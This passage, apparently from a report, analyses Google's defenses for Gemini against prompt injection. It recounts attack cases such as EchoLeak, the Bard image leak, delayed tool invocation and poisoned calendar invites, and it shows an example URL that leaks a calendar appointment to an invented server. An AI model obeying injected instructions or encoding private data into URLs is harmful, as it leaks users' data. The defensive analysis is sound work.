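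Reminders are weakest when the user lets retrieved content decide what the agent should do. Ma and colleagues separated requests that fully specify an action from open-ended ones such as "do everything on my to-do list". With the reminder in place, adaptive attacks on DeepSeek-v4-Flash succeeded in 0.8 percent of the fully specified cases and 25 percent of the open-ended ones. There were only 24 open-ended cases, so the exact figure means little, but a gap is to be expected because the user's request to follow instructions in a document conflicts with the reminder not to. To be useful, the agent has to disregard the reminder for the user's own items and work out which items those are.

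## Blocking images and suspicious links

When an injection gets past both the classifier and the reminder, an attacker who wants private data still has to get it out of the user's account. Gemini could send the data out with a tool call, such as sending an email, but displaying an answer can also send data to an outside server. Google's third defense therefore acts on the answer after Gemini has written it.

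### How a picture can carry a message

Gemini can put an image into an answer by giving the picture's web address in Markdown. The app turns this into part of the page, and the user's browser then asks the server at that address for the picture. The request includes the address itself. Suppose Gemini answers a question about next week and includes an image at this invented address:

`https://images.example/dot.png?note=dentist-tuesday-3pm`

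The text after the question mark is a parameter. Websites ordinarily use parameters for things like search terms and page numbers, but this one contains an appointment from the user's calendar. As soon as the answer appears, the browser contacts the server, and whoever runs that server can read the appointment in its log. The server doesn't have to send back a picture. According to *Securing Workspace GenAI at Google*, the user may see only a broken image icon.

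The attacker doesn't need to know about the dentist in advance. The injection only has to get the model to fill in that part of the URL from whatever it has read. Since the model writes the text and the browser sends the data, restricting the model's tools wouldn't prevent the leak.

A link can carry the same text as an image, but it leaks data only if the user clicks it, whereas an image leaks data whenever the assistant follows the injection. Needing a click is an obstacle for the attacker, though perhaps not a large one, because the link appears in an answer the user asked for and the attacker can choose its label.

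*Trust No AI* (2024) describes such a case in Microsoft 365 Copilot, Microsoft's counterpart to Workspace with Gemini. A phishing email made Copilot search the user's inbox for sensitive information and hide it in a clickable link using invisible characters. A researcher found the flaw in February 2024 and reported it to Microsoft, which fixed it that July. Amazon dealt with a similar problem in its business assistant, Amazon Q, by making links unclickable.

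Gemini has also had a problem with links. *Gemini Search Personalization Model* (2025), by the security company Tenable, describes how a malicious web page could plant queries in a user's search history, which Gemini read to personalize its answers. Gemini displayed a link containing information it had saved about the user, and clicking it would have sent that information to the attacker. Google mitigated the problem in July 2025, a month after it described its link defenses.

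### The Bard leak of 2023

Google had learned about image leaks from a flaw in its own chatbot. In September 2023 it gave Bard, later renamed Gemini, access to users' Gmail, Docs and Drive. *Hacking Google Bard*, a post on the security blog Embrace The Red, soon showed that a shared Google Doc could carry a prompt injection into the conversation. In the demonstration, Bard put part of the user's chat history into an image address, and the browser sent that data out by loading the image, without the user clicking anything.

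Bard already had a Content Security Policy that should have prevented this. Such a policy tells the browser which sources a page may load images and other content from. Bard's policy blocked images from arbitrary servers, including the attacker's own. But it allowed addresses across Google's own domains, where Google lets customers run small programs, and one of those programs could receive the request and record the data. Willison pointed out in *Hacking Google Bard* that this kind of attack is inevitable whenever a system combines access to private data with exposure to untrusted text.

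Embrace The Red reported the flaw on 19 September 2023, and Google confirmed a fix on 19 October but didn't explain it. Bard still displayed images afterward and the policy hadn't changed, so Embrace The Red guessed that Google was now filtering out addresses with data in them.

The problem came back in 2024 in AI Studio, Google's website for developers to try its models. Embrace The Red got the model to write the image in HTML, the code used to build web pages, instead of Markdown. A series of invisible one-pixel images could send more data. Google fixed it within 24 hours of a public complaint by displaying the image code as plain text, so the browser never requested the picture.

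### EchoLeak

The best-known image leak is EchoLeak, a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot that researchers at Aim Labs reported in January 2025. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*, Microsoft finished the patch in May and the researchers published their findings on 11 June, two days before Google's post on its five defenses.

The attacker only had to send an email. If the email seemed relevant to something the user later asked Copilot, Copilot retrieved it along with the user's own material, and the answer sent private data to the attacker. The researchers called this a zero-click attack because the user didn't have to open the email or click on anything.

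Copilot had several layers of defense, and Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, explains how the attack got past each:

- A classifier screened emails for injections. It missed this one because the instructions seemed to be meant for the person receiving the email and never mentioned an AI.
- A filter removed outside links and images from the answer. It recognized the usual way of writing them in Markdown but missed a less common way that the app still displayed.
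- A Content Security Policy restricted where images could come from. One of the allowed Microsoft addresses belonged to a service that would fetch an outside page on request, so it passed the data along.

*EchoLeak (2025)*, an academic case study, calls this the first known case of a prompt injection weaponized to take data from an AI system in real use. The Bard demonstration came earlier, but it required the user to bring the malicious document into the conversation, which Ravia considers an important difference. Microsoft confirmed that EchoLeak affected no customers, so "weaponized" doesn't mean that criminals used it.

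The last step is much like the Bard leak. In both cases the browser enforced its list of allowed addresses, but the list was based on the false assumption that a company controls everything that happens on its domain. Microsoft and Google both run services that carry out requests from outsiders, and one unsuitable service on an allowed domain is enough to defeat the restriction.

### Why Google blocks the images altogether

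Google says that because its Markdown sanitizer doesn't display external images, EchoLeak's zero-click image leak is "not applicable to Gemini". The reasoning is sound, because a browser that never requests an image can't leak data through the request, regardless of the site's reputation or how the attacker disguised the data.

Blocking external images is a much stronger defense than a classifier or a reminder to the model. The sanitizer applies a fixed rule that doesn't depend on what the text means or what the attacker intended, so no wording in an injection can create an exception. Google can use such a strict rule because people seldom need a picture from an outside server in a summary of their email.

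The rule still depends on two details that Google hasn't explained. One is what counts as "external". The Bard leak went through Google's own domain, so a sanitizer that treated every Google address as internal would miss the same kind of leak. The other is whether the sanitizer recognizes every way of writing an image that the app can display. EchoLeak and the AI Studio leak both exploited an unusual format. The sanitizer has to interpret an answer exactly as the program that displays it does.

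Outside evidence mostly supports Google. Tenable researchers looking for leaks report in *The Trifecta* that Gemini filtered or restricted images and links and cut off suspicious answers. Adversa AI's *Google Workspace Gemini Agent Security Risks*, a security vendor's rating page, cites research by Buganizer.cc in which the Markdown sanitization failed without the user clicking anything. This secondhand account doesn't establish how the bypass worked or whether it still works, but given the history, a formatting trick would not be surprising.

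The sanitizer also doesn't protect every Google product. Gemini Enterprise, a separate product that searches a company's data, had a flaw called GeminiJack that let stolen data leave in what looked like a harmless image request, according to TechRepublic's *GeminiJack Zero-Click Flaw Exposed Millions of Users in Google Workspace AI*. The security company Noma reported it in June 2025, the month of Google's post, and SC Media reports that the two companies had resolved it by November. A year later, 0DIN's *Faking the Pipeline* showed that Antigravity, Google's coding tool, still displayed images from outside servers and could leak a secret key that way. The two cases suggest that Google had to block such images product by product, even though it had known about this type of leak since 2023, but they aren't evidence of a vulnerability in Gmail or Docs.

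### What happens to a suspicious link

Gemini has to keep some links and remove others, so Google can't treat links as it treats images. A user who asks for a summary of an email about a meeting may want the link to join it, and the assistant would be much less useful without any links.

The link check uses Google Safe Browsing, which identifies sites involved in phishing or malware and warns people in many browsers before they visit one. If Gemini's summary of an email thread contains an unsafe link, the user sees "suspicious link removed" in its place and can still read the rest of the summary. When a safe link is flagged by mistake, the user loses only that link, whereas a mistake by the content classifier can remove a whole email.

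Gavish classes URL sanitization as a deterministic defense, meaning it applies fixed rules instead of having a model interpret the text. As with the image rule, an attacker can't get around it with persuasive wording, but its effectiveness depends on the quality of the information the rules use.

That information is useful against ordinary phishing. Suppose one of the 20 unread emails in the earlier example links to a fake bank page that Safe Browsing already lists. Gemini might repeat the link in its summary because of an injection, or just because the link seemed important. Redacting the link helps in both cases and doesn't require detecting an injection.

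A new fake shop is harder to catch because it may not have a bad record yet. Android Authority reported in 2025 that the researcher Markopoulos had used hidden text in an email to make Gemini recommend a malicious site selling discounted phones. Google reportedly decided that this wasn't a security bug. A reputation check tends to have little information about this kind of site, but Android Authority didn't say whether Safe Browsing had checked it, so the case doesn't clearly show that URL redaction failed.

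### A good reputation is the wrong test for a leak

Reputation is even less useful when the link carries stolen data. The attacker needs only a server that logs the addresses requested from it, as practically all servers do. The site itself can be harmless to visit, with no malware or fake login page, so Safe Browsing would have no reason to list it. The danger is in the address Gemini wrote, which has the user's appointment at the end.

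SafeBreach's *Gemini's Secret Affair* (2026) gives a rare outside view of how Google applies these checks. A SafeBreach researcher tested Gemini's voice assistant on Android, which has a tool for opening web addresses. Gemini refused to open addresses that Safe Browsing classed as unsafe or didn't recognize. It also seemed to refuse addresses with added parameters, even when the site itself was rated safe.

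The second refusal is a sensible precaution against leaks, and it would stop the dentist example whatever the server's reputation. But it's incomplete, because an address can also carry information outside its parameters. In 0DIN's Antigravity demonstration, the secret was in the main part of the address. The refusal would also be hard to apply to links in a Gmail summary, where a link may need its parameter to open the right booking or document. Refusing to open such links automatically is a small inconvenience, but removing them from every summary would annoy people constantly.

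SafeBreach then found that a link rated safe could still redirect the browser to a different address. In the test, Gemini accepted an address with a good reputation and followed its redirect without asking the user. The redirect opened the phone's Zoom app, which joined a meeting and began streaming video. SafeBreach simulated the redirect on the test phone with a local server, and its real website never sent anyone to Zoom.

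The researcher, Or Yair, argues that a safe rating is easy to get because a site receives one automatically after staying harmless for a while. According to his explanation in The Hacker News, Gemini trusted the site because of its clean record and then followed a later redirect. Google could improve this defense by checking each new address in the chain, including whether it opens a web page or another app. *Securing Workspace GenAI at Google* recommends restricting the types of link that an assistant may display, which would stop a direct link to an app but not a web link that redirects to one.

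These observations concern a phone tool that opens addresses itself, and Gemini may handle links in Gmail summaries differently. Google received SafeBreach's report in August 2025 and improved its content classifier before SafeBreach published. In November, Google confirmed that the improvements had mitigated the attacks. They stop the injections SafeBreach used from reaching the tool, but SafeBreach doesn't report any change to how Gemini follows redirects.

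### Checking where the link came from

OpenAI uses a different test for addresses that its agents open automatically. Gend's *AI agent link safety* explains that an agent may load an address if an independent index shows that this exact address already exists on the public web. Otherwise, the user gets a warning and can decide whether to open it. An address containing private information, such as somebody's dentist appointment, is very unlikely to be in the index, even if the rest of the site is. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, the researcher who had reported ChatGPT's image leak nearly three years earlier welcomed OpenAI's openness about the defense.

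Checking whether links appear in a public index would be awkward for email because so many of the links people receive are private. Links to shared documents, plane tickets and password resets shouldn't be in a public index, and if each one triggered a warning, users would soon learn to ignore warnings.

*Securing Workspace GenAI at Google* lists link grounding, which suits email better. It removes any URL in the model's answer that doesn't appear in the material the model was given. A genuine ticket link appears in the airline's email, so it stays. The attacker's email may contain the start of a URL, but the version with the user's appointment added appears only in Gemini's answer, so the check removes it. Link grounding is described as part of a recommended design, and it is unclear whether Gmail uses it.

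Safe Browsing would still be needed alongside link grounding, because a phishing link copied from an email has a source and would pass the grounding check. The checks would handle four kinds of link roughly as follows.

| Link in the answer | Safe Browsing | Public-index test | Link grounding |
|---|---|---|---|
| Known phishing page, copied from an email | Removes it | May allow it | Allows it |
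| Harmless-looking site, with private data added by the model | Allows it | Warns the user | Removes it |
| Harmless-looking site that redirects elsewhere, copied from an email | May allow it | May allow it | Allows it |
| Genuine private ticket link, copied from an email | Allows it | Warns the user | Allows it |

*Expected results, based on how each check works and not on tests.*

Even combined, these checks leave a small leak. If an email contains several complete web addresses, the attacker can learn something from which one ends up in the answer. With *N* addresses to choose from, a single visit reveals at most log₂ *N* bits. A choice among 16 addresses gives four bits, and a nine-digit passport number contains about 30, so the attacker would need eight visits to learn it. Eight images could trigger those visits in an instant, but few people would click eight odd links in a row, so blocking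 images makes the leak much less serious.

The security company Checkmarx demonstrated a zero-click leak in Microsoft's Copilot Chat. It says Microsoft didn't consider the leak a vulnerability or commit to fixing it. Checkmarx therefore expected no fix for the version that needs a click, and contrasted Microsoft's response with Gemini's ban on external images.

### Leaks and lies without a link

Markdown sanitization and URL redaction only affect what they detect in the displayed answer. They couldn't have stopped the attack Miggo found, which put the private data in a calendar event instead.

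They can't catch a false statement either, such as a fake security alert that gives the user a phone number instead of a link. Security Boulevard's *Google Gemini AI Flaw Could Lead to Gmail Compromise, Phishing* (2025) notes that the email that produces such an alert needs no links or attachments.

Gemini can also contact a server without displaying anything. Because Google had restricted images and links so thoroughly, Tenable's researchers turned to the tool Gemini uses to read web pages. Tenable's *Gemini Browsing Tool* reports that an injection could make Gemini use this tool to open an address containing the user's saved information and location. Gemini didn't ask for confirmation, and the defenses against image and link leaks didn't apply because the tool sent the request before there was an answer to clean. Google has since blocked this leak, but the same problem can arise with any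 tool that sends information out.

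## Limits on which tools retrieved text can set off

Google also limits what Gemini may do after it reads other people's text, because a tool call can do harm before Gemini has written an answer to clean. These limits weren't among the five defenses in the June 2025 post. In April 2026, Gavish called them "tool chaining policies", meaning fixed rules about which tool calls may follow others. The problem they address predates the 2025 post and comes mostly from how Gemini is built.

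### One model in charge of several agents

*Invitation Is All You Need!* (Nassi, Cohen and Yair, 2025) describes the structure behind Gemini's web app, mobile app and the Gemini-powered Google Assistant. A central model, the orchestrator, talks to the user and plans the steps for each request. It passes each step to an agent, a part of the system with its own tools. For example, the Calendar agent can list, create and delete events, and the Google Home agent controls lights, heating and connected windows. On Android phones, a Utilities agent can open web addresses and other apps.

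Only the orchestrator can start an agent, so the Calendar agent can't call the Home agent. Each agent also keeps its working context private and passes only its output to the orchestrator. If an injection took over the Calendar agent, these restrictions should confine the damage to the calendar.

The Calendar agent's output can itself carry an injection. When a user asks about the week's events, the agent returns their titles, and a stranger may have written one of them. The orchestrator then reads that title, and it can start every other agent. The attacker doesn't need to fool the Calendar agent, because the agent passes the instruction along just by copying the title accurately.

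Isolation would work better if agents could return only a time or a yes-or-no answer, because neither can easily carry an instruction. Such answers would be enough for "am I free on Tuesday?" but not for "what's on my calendar?" or for an email summary, which has to draw on the email's words.

### An instruction that waits

Google had anticipated part of this problem by November 2023, when the researcher behind Embrace The Red tested Bard. Once untrusted content had entered the conversation, Bard would not, for the rest of that turn (one user message and the response to it), call the extension that read the user's mail and files. It would still call the extensions for flights, hotels and YouTube, which held nothing private. Embrace The Red's *Google Gemini* called this an interesting approach that other vendors had not yet adopted.

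However, the restriction lasted only until the end of the turn. Embrace The Red got around it with an email containing an instruction for Gemini to follow when the user next sent a message, a technique called delayed tool invocation. Gemini's summary of the email put the instruction into the conversation. When the user sent another message, Gemini fetched a Drive document the user hadn't asked for.

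A rule against immediate chaining misses this because it checks only whether a tool call follows untrusted content within one turn. In the next turn, the latest input is a genuine message from the user, so the tool call appears to respond to it. But the untrusted content stays in the prompt for the rest of the conversation.

*The Promptware Kill Chain* (Brodt, Feldman and colleagues, 2026) describes the same weakness in plan-then-execute, a design in which an agent plans its steps before reading untrusted content so that the content can't add new ones. But the user's next message requires a new plan, and the orchestrator writes it with the planted instruction already in the conversation.

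The early demonstration did little harm because the document appeared only in the user's own chat, and Google had already fixed the image leak that could have sent it elsewhere. Embrace The Red warned that the technique would become serious if Gemini gained tools that could write or post content. In December 2024 the same researcher reported that, with this technique, a document could make Gemini save false facts in its long-term memory, which carries over into later conversations. According to Embrace The Red's *Hacking Gemini's Memory with Prompt Injection and Delayed Tool Invocation*, Google rated the attack's likelihood and impact as low.

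### Fourteen scenarios

Nassi, Cohen and Yair reported their findings to Google on 22 February 2025 and presented them at the Black Hat security conference that August. The attacks required only the target's email address and an ordinary computer. Most placed the injection in the title of a calendar invitation, though the researchers also used email subject lines. The user later asked Gemini an everyday question about their schedule or inbox. Many of the actions ran only after the user then replied with something as ordinary as "thanks".

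| Class of attack | Scenarios, with the researchers' risk ratings |
|---|---|
| Poisoning one conversation | Abusive messages (high), spam (medium), phishing (very high) |
| Poisoning long-term memory | Disinformation (low) |
| Misusing tools of the agent that read the text | Deleting or adding calendar events (medium) |
| Starting a different agent | Opening windows (critical), turning on a boiler (high), switching lights (high) |
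| Starting an app on the phone | Downloading a file (medium), locating the user (high), streaming video through Zoom (critical), leaking meeting titles (very high), leaking emails (critical), a self-spreading worm (critical) |

*The 14 scenarios in Invitation Is All You Need!*

Deleting an event required only the Calendar agent, which had a legitimate reason to be running. To open a window, the instruction had to pass from the Calendar agent through the orchestrator to the Home agent. Brodt and colleagues call this lateral movement, the term for an intruder moving from one computer to others on a network. The last class, which worked only on Android, goes further because Gemini opens a browser or Zoom, and that app then acts with its own permissions.

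The researchers leaked data by having Gemini open a web address that contained the titles of six meetings. The email version of the attack leaked the subject of one message. The "critical" rating for leaked emails suggests a larger leak than the researchers achieved, though a subject line can be private.

Three of the 14 scenarios also rest on less evidence than the others. For disinformation, Nassi and colleagues rely on Embrace The Red's memory attack without repeating it. They infer that phishing would work because they got Gemini to display a spam link. The worm is a proposal to use the email leak to collect the victim's contacts and send them the injection.

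A malicious invitation also stays in the calendar after the conversation ends, so Gemini may retrieve it again if the user opens a new chat and asks about the same week.

The paper lists Google's five defenses and notes that they "were ineffective or weren't deployed" when the study took place. If a classifier wasn't running, a successful attack is no evidence of how well it works. The study is strong evidence of what an injection could do with Gemini's tools in early 2025, but it isn't a test of the five defenses.

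### Where the 73 percent comes from

In the study's best-known finding, 73 percent of the threats posed a high to critical risk. The researchers adapted their scoring from ISO/SAE 21434, a cybersecurity standard for cars. They rated each threat's impact on the user's money, daily life, safety and privacy, and kept the worst of the four ratings. For likelihood, they averaged six factors, each scored from 0 to 3. They then used a grid to convert impact and likelihood into a risk level.

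Nearly all the attacks have the same likelihood, because the attacker does much the same thing each time. By the paper's definitions, a laptop earns 3 points, a computing graduate's skills 2, freedom to attack at any time 3, needing only the target's email address 2, less than a day of preparation 3, and a common user request as the trigger 2. The average is

(3 + 2 + 3 + 2 + 3 + 2) / 6 = 2.5,

and anything from 2.4 up counts as "very likely". Phishing scores lower because the victim must also type in their details.

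"Very likely" here means "easy to attempt". The score doesn't measure how many people try such attacks or how often Gemini follows a given injection. Andy Wen, a security director for Google Workspace, told WIRED in *Hackers Hijacked Google's Gemini AI With a Poisoned Calendar Invite* (2025) that real-world prompt injections were "exceedingly rare". That could be true even if the attacks were as easy as the researchers say.

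The 73 percent differs slightly from the figure the paper's own list gives, though not by enough to matter. The list has four critical risks, two very high and four high, which makes 10 of 14, or 71 percent. The researchers may have counted 11 of 15, or 73 percent, because the summary table gives the Zoom attack two rows, one for the invitation and one for the email version.

The impact ratings matter more than the likelihood ratings. If each attack scored one point less on one of the six likelihood factors, the usual average would fall from 2.5 to about 2.3, which counts as "likely". Some risks would drop from critical to very high, but the same ten would still be high or above. Switching on someone's lights counts as a "moderate" impact because it affects their home, and a moderate impact combined with an easy attack gives a high risk, though many people would call it a nuisance. They would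 probably agree with the critical rating for opening the windows, which the researchers gave because someone could photograph the user at home. Open windows might also let in a burglar.

Google and the researchers also disagreed about how easily a stranger could deliver the invitation. Google Calendar can add invitations from everyone, only from known senders, or only after the user responds. Wen said the researchers had changed the default setting. They answered that some of the attacks arrived through an email subject or a document title, which the calendar setting doesn't affect. The setting also gives little protection against known senders, such as a colleague or an estranged spouse, whom the paper treats as plausible attackers.

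### Google's reply and a second round

Google asked the researchers to include a statement in the paper. In it, Google says that their report led to a "focused, high-priority effort" and lists three kinds of improvement: wider use of confirmation prompts for sensitive actions, stricter handling of web addresses, and content classifiers to detect injections. Google also says it reran the original attacks with many variations and confirmed that the defenses were robust against them, but it gives no success rates.

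The statement calls the techniques "theoretical", although the researchers had recorded the attacks on video using their own accounts. But Wen told WIRED that Google took the vulnerabilities "extremely seriously" and that the research had accelerated its rollout of defenses. In his 2026 talk, *Securing Workspace GenAI at Google*, Lidzborski acknowledged that Google had protected users' data but overlooked what Gemini could do in their homes.

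Google didn't mention tool chaining in its reply, but Yair found a change when he retested Gemini for SafeBreach, this time through notifications from messaging apps. Gemini now refused plain delayed tool invocation in every attempt. It would open a window if the user requested it, or if the user said yes right after Gemini asked whether to open it. Yair inferred that a check compared the user's reply with Gemini's previous message to see whether the reply made sense as permission. Google hasn't confirmed how the check worked.

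This check improved on a rule that expired after one turn, but an injection could still influence Gemini's previous message, which was half of the evidence for the user's consent. Yair made Gemini ask for permission in a way that satisfied the check but the user was unlikely to notice or understand. The user thought they were answering a harmless question, and their reply authorized the action.

The new technique restored most of the effects from the first study. It also let Yair save a false memory and schedule a recurring task, neither of which the calendar attacks had achieved. Embrace The Red had already changed Gemini's memory with plain delayed invocation in late 2024, so Google may have tightened the memory tool before the calendar attacks. The Hacker News (2026) reports no evidence that anyone used the new technique against real users. The fix Google confirmed was a better content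 classifier, so it used a learned detector to make up for a weakness in the check on tool calls.

### The Policy Engine

By April 2026, Google was managing its fixed rules centrally. Gavish describes a Policy Engine that holds the settings for basic tool calls, tool chaining and URL sanitization. He doesn't list the rules themselves.

In the general design that Díaz and colleagues describe, the engine runs outside the model and intercepts each tool call before it runs. It checks how risky the action is, the current context, and what the agent did earlier, including whether the agent recently processed untrusted data. It can then allow the call, block it, or require the user's approval. In one of their examples, an agent that has just read material from a suspicious source can't send email outside the organization unless the user approves.

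In principle, such a rule can stop delayed tool invocation, provided "recently" covers the whole time that the untrusted text remains in the conversation. Embrace The Red recommends this version of the rule, with confirmation required for every sensitive tool call once untrusted data has entered a chat. But nearly every useful Workspace conversation starts with Gemini reading an email, a file or an invitation, so a strict rule would apply almost all the time, and users would have to approve actions they had clearly requested.

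The engine can be more selective if it tracks where data came from. *Securing Workspace GenAI at Google* recommends recording a conversation's risk level as new data arrives and restricting later tool calls accordingly. One suggested rule blocks requests to outside websites after the agent has read Workspace data. Such a rule would have stopped the leak through Gemini's browsing tool if it had also covered the user's saved information. But it would also stop Gemini from looking up the opening hours of a restaurant named in an email.

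### Fixed rules and learned detectors

Google can change a fixed rule faster than it can retrain a model. Gavish says that simple configuration updates allow quick "point fixes" for immediate threats, whereas a new classifier needs training data, training and evaluation. If researchers report that text in a calendar event can make Gemini open a home's windows, Google can immediately block the use of the calendar and window controls together, then retrain the classifier later.

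A fixed rule is also more predictable than a classifier, because nobody can list in advance which injections a classifier will miss. The engine reaches the same decision every time the tool call and recorded history are the same, so engineers can test it and administrators can audit it.

This advantage depends on what the rule examines. A rule that stops Gemini from opening a window after it reads an outsider's invitation works however the invitation is worded. Gavish's example of a quick fix, a "regex takedown", is also deterministic, but it blocks only text that matches a particular pattern, so an attacker can get around it by rewording the request. It is useful against a known attack for a few days and much less useful after that.

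Learned detectors have broader coverage than rules because they can recognize an attack that uses a combination of tools nobody thought to restrict. The number of combinations also grows quickly, and 40 tools allow 1,600 sequences of two calls and 64,000 sequences of three. Engineers can reduce the number of cases rules must cover by grouping tools by what they do, such as reading outside text, reading private data, or sending or changing something. Díaz and colleagues recommend describing actions this way so that security software can identify which ones change something or handle sensitive data.

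Grouping doesn't separate legitimate actions from attacks that use the same sequence of tool calls, though. Díaz and colleagues give the example of an agent that reads a document and then sends an email, which may be what the user wanted or may be theft. The attack Miggo found had the same ambiguity, because Gemini read the calendar and then created an event. Requiring approval for the new event would have interrupted the attack, but it would also interrupt someone who asked Gemini to find a free hour and book it.

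### The controls that the researchers proposed

Nassi and colleagues suggest several controls, including isolating the agents' contexts and letting only the orchestrator start agents. By their own account, Gemini already had these two restrictions. The restrictions may be worth keeping, but the attacks succeeded despite them.

The researchers would also require confirmation whenever an agent uses a second tool during one inference (a single run of the model). This would have caught Gemini deleting an event immediately after listing the calendar, but not a delayed action, which happens in a later run. For delayed actions, they propose stopping the assistant from starting agents or saving memories after a tool has brought in outside data.

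Simple filters would check for offensive language and for the @ sign, which the researchers say is needed to call an agent by name. Email addresses also contain @, so a usable filter would have to check for it next to an agent's name.

One proposed defense is to run the request twice, once with the outside data and once without it, and ask the user for confirmation if the outcomes differ. Suppose a stranger's calendar invitation contains an injected instruction to open a window, and the user thanks Gemini after hearing the week's events. Without the invitation, Gemini replies politely, but with it, Gemini tries to open the window. The difference reveals the attack without the need to recognize malicious wording, however many turns pass before the injection takes effect.

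The comparison is less useful when outside data is supposed to change the outcome. If a user asks Gemini to add the flight from an airline's email to the calendar, Gemini can't create the event without reading the email, so the runs with and without the email will always differ. The researchers also recommend the method against spam and phishing in Gemini's answers, but a summary written with the emails will differ from one written without them. Comparing only the tool calls would avoid that problem but miss a false sentence in the answer. Running the model twice also costs more and could delay the answer.

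With a combination of these controls in place, Nassi and colleagues estimate that every risk would fall to between very low and medium. This is their judgment and not a measurement, since they didn't build the controls and attack them. They assume that an attacker would now need a cluster of graphics processors, expert knowledge of AI, detailed knowledge of the defenses and several months of preparation. The new likelihood score is

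(1 + 1 + 3 + 0 + 0 + 2) / 6 ≈ 1.17,

which counts as "unlikely" because it is below 1.2. One more point on any factor would raise it to 1.33, or "moderately likely", and the Zoom, window and email attacks would return to high risk. The estimate therefore depends on small differences between guesses.

Yair's second study also suggests that the assumptions are optimistic. He is one of the three authors, so he was not a typical attacker, but he worked out Google's new check from the outside by trial and error. He reported the bypass on 17 August 2025, less than two months after Google sent its statement for the first paper. The bypass suggests that an attacker may not need special hardware or inside knowledge, but it doesn't refute the estimate, because Google hadn't deployed the exact set of controls that the paper proposed.

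### Giving each task only the tools it needs

General rules about chaining tools are hard to write because Gemini has many tools and most requests need only a few. An injection can't make an assistant use a tool it doesn't have.

Google applies this idea in Workspace Studio, a product for building automated workflows called flows. Quinney (2026) explains in *Defend against agentic risks with multi-layered protections in Google Workspace Studio* that each flow gets its own identity with only the permissions its task requires. A flow that sends email through Gmail has no access to Drive or Chat, so an injection in a message can't make it open the owner's files. Administrators can also set rules that block a step or require approval, depending on the data the flow has used and who could see the result. These rules are still needed because a flow that can read and send email could leak an inbox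 without any other permissions.

A flow's job is known in advance, but someone chatting with Gemini in Gmail might ask for anything. *Contextual Agent Security* (2025) describes Conseca, a framework that writes a new policy for each request. The policy generator receives the user's request, descriptions of the available tools and trusted context. A separate enforcer then checks every proposed action against the policy. If the enforcer rejects an action, it returns a reason, and the agent can propose another action or ask the user to confirm.

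For a request to summarize 20 emails, a good policy would let Gemini read mail and do nothing else. An injection could still influence the summary, but it couldn't create an event or open a web address. Delayed invocation should also fail if the system writes a new policy for each message, because a user who says "thanks" hasn't asked for anything that requires a tool. The policy generator could still make mistakes, but a stranger's email couldn't make it write a looser policy as long as the email stayed out of the trusted context.

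Vague requests are as difficult for the generator as for the user-instruction classifier, because neither reads the emails that determine which actions are needed. *Surviving the Perfect Storm* (2026), the companion page to Lidzborski's talk, lists Conseca among its recommended resources, but Google hasn't said whether Workspace with Gemini uses it.

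## Asking the user to confirm an action

A rule about tool calls can allow an action, block it or leave the decision to the user. The user confirmation framework, the fourth of Google's five defenses, handles the last case. Gemini prepares the action, shows the user what it will do, and waits for explicit approval.

Google gives the example of a user who asks the Gemini app to delete all of Saturday's events. Gemini finds three in Google Calendar, displays their details and asks the user to confirm before deleting them. Google says such risky operations "may" trigger a confirmation request, so it doesn't promise one for every deletion.

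The user in this example wanted the events deleted, so the confirmation request mostly protects against an ordinary mistake, such as Gemini picking the wrong Saturday. An unexpected confirmation request is a strong sign of an injection. An attack that changes one detail of something the user did ask for is much harder to notice, because the user expects a confirmation request and this one looks roughly right.

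### Which actions need approval

Google extended the framework after researchers showed that a calendar invitation could take control of Gemini's tools. In its full June 2025 statement for the paper by Nassi and colleagues, Google said it now broadly required approval for risky operations involving Workspace data, interactions between apps, or control of devices. It didn't list the operations.

Later documents are more specific, but the rules differ by product. Google's *Create content, schedule events, and coordinate tasks across Workspace* (2026) covers the version of Gemini that works across Gmail, Docs, Drive, Slides and Chat. Google's *Use Gemini Spark to manage your tasks and workflows in Gemini Apps* covers Spark, an experimental agent that carries out longer tasks, some of them scheduled. Google's help page *Create & manage your calendar events with Gemini Apps* covers the Gemini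 app's ordinary calendar functions.

| Action | Approval beforehand |
|---|---|
| Sending an email or scheduling a meeting from a Workspace app | Yes, on a preview card that the user can edit |
| Editing a shared document, spreadsheet or presentation with Spark | Yes, after reviewing the planned edits |
| Adding several events that Gemini found in one email | Yes |
| Deleting calendar events in the Gemini app | Sometimes, as in the Saturday example |
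| Creating one calendar event in the Gemini app | None described, but the user can undo it |
| Creating a new document, spreadsheet or presentation from a Workspace app | None described |
| Adding, changing or deleting a task from Gmail | None described |
| Changing or deleting private tasks in bulk with Spark | No |

*Approval rules in Google's announcements and help pages, mostly from 2026.*

Gemini may still ask for confirmation where the table has "none described". For instance, Google's help page for Gmail describes no approval step for scheduling a lunch break, but the preview card announced in September 2026 may cover it. Google explicitly says Gemini won't ask only for bulk changes to private tasks, and it advises users to review what they have typed before submitting it. This can help users catch their own mistakes, but it doesn't help against an injection, because the attacker's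 instruction isn't in the text the user reviews.

Google mostly asks users to confirm actions that will affect other people, which makes sense because a user can't take back an email once someone has read it. Calendar events are harder to classify because outsiders can sometimes read them, as in the attack Miggo found. Private items can also do harm. If an injection adds a false reminder to a user's task list, the user may later assume they wrote it.

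Google's other agents have their own confirmation rules. Google's *Use Gemini Agent for multi-step tasks in Gemini Apps* describes an agent for personal accounts that asks before sending messages, changing data or scheduling events. On Android, Gemini can operate other companies' apps. According to Google's *Ask Gemini to handle your multi-step tasks in select Android apps*, Gemini aims to ask before messaging a driver or changing a delivery address in these apps, but it might place an order without confirmation.

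Workspace Studio, the product for automated flows, requires approval by default for any step that shares data outside the organization. Google's *Require approval for flows* explains that administrators can turn this requirement off. According to Quinney, the flow's owner finds pending requests on a separate approvals page.

Google's help pages say that Gemini "is designed to ask" or "aims to ask" before certain actions. This wording may just be legal caution, but if it means that the model itself decides when to ask, that would be a serious weakness, because an injection could stop it from asking. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) mentions a safety researcher who told an open-source agent to confirm before acting. The agent started deleting messages from her real inbox anyway and didn't stop when she told it to. A confirmation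 is dependable if software outside the model blocks the tool call until the user approves it, as in the general design that Díaz and colleagues describe.

### When a "yes" counts as consent

If a user asks Gemini to email a signed lease to their landlord, an injection in another message could make Gemini fill in a different address. Gemini asks the user to confirm before sending. The user's approval is only meaningful if they notice the request, understand it and can see the actual email and recipient. The approval must also apply only to that email.

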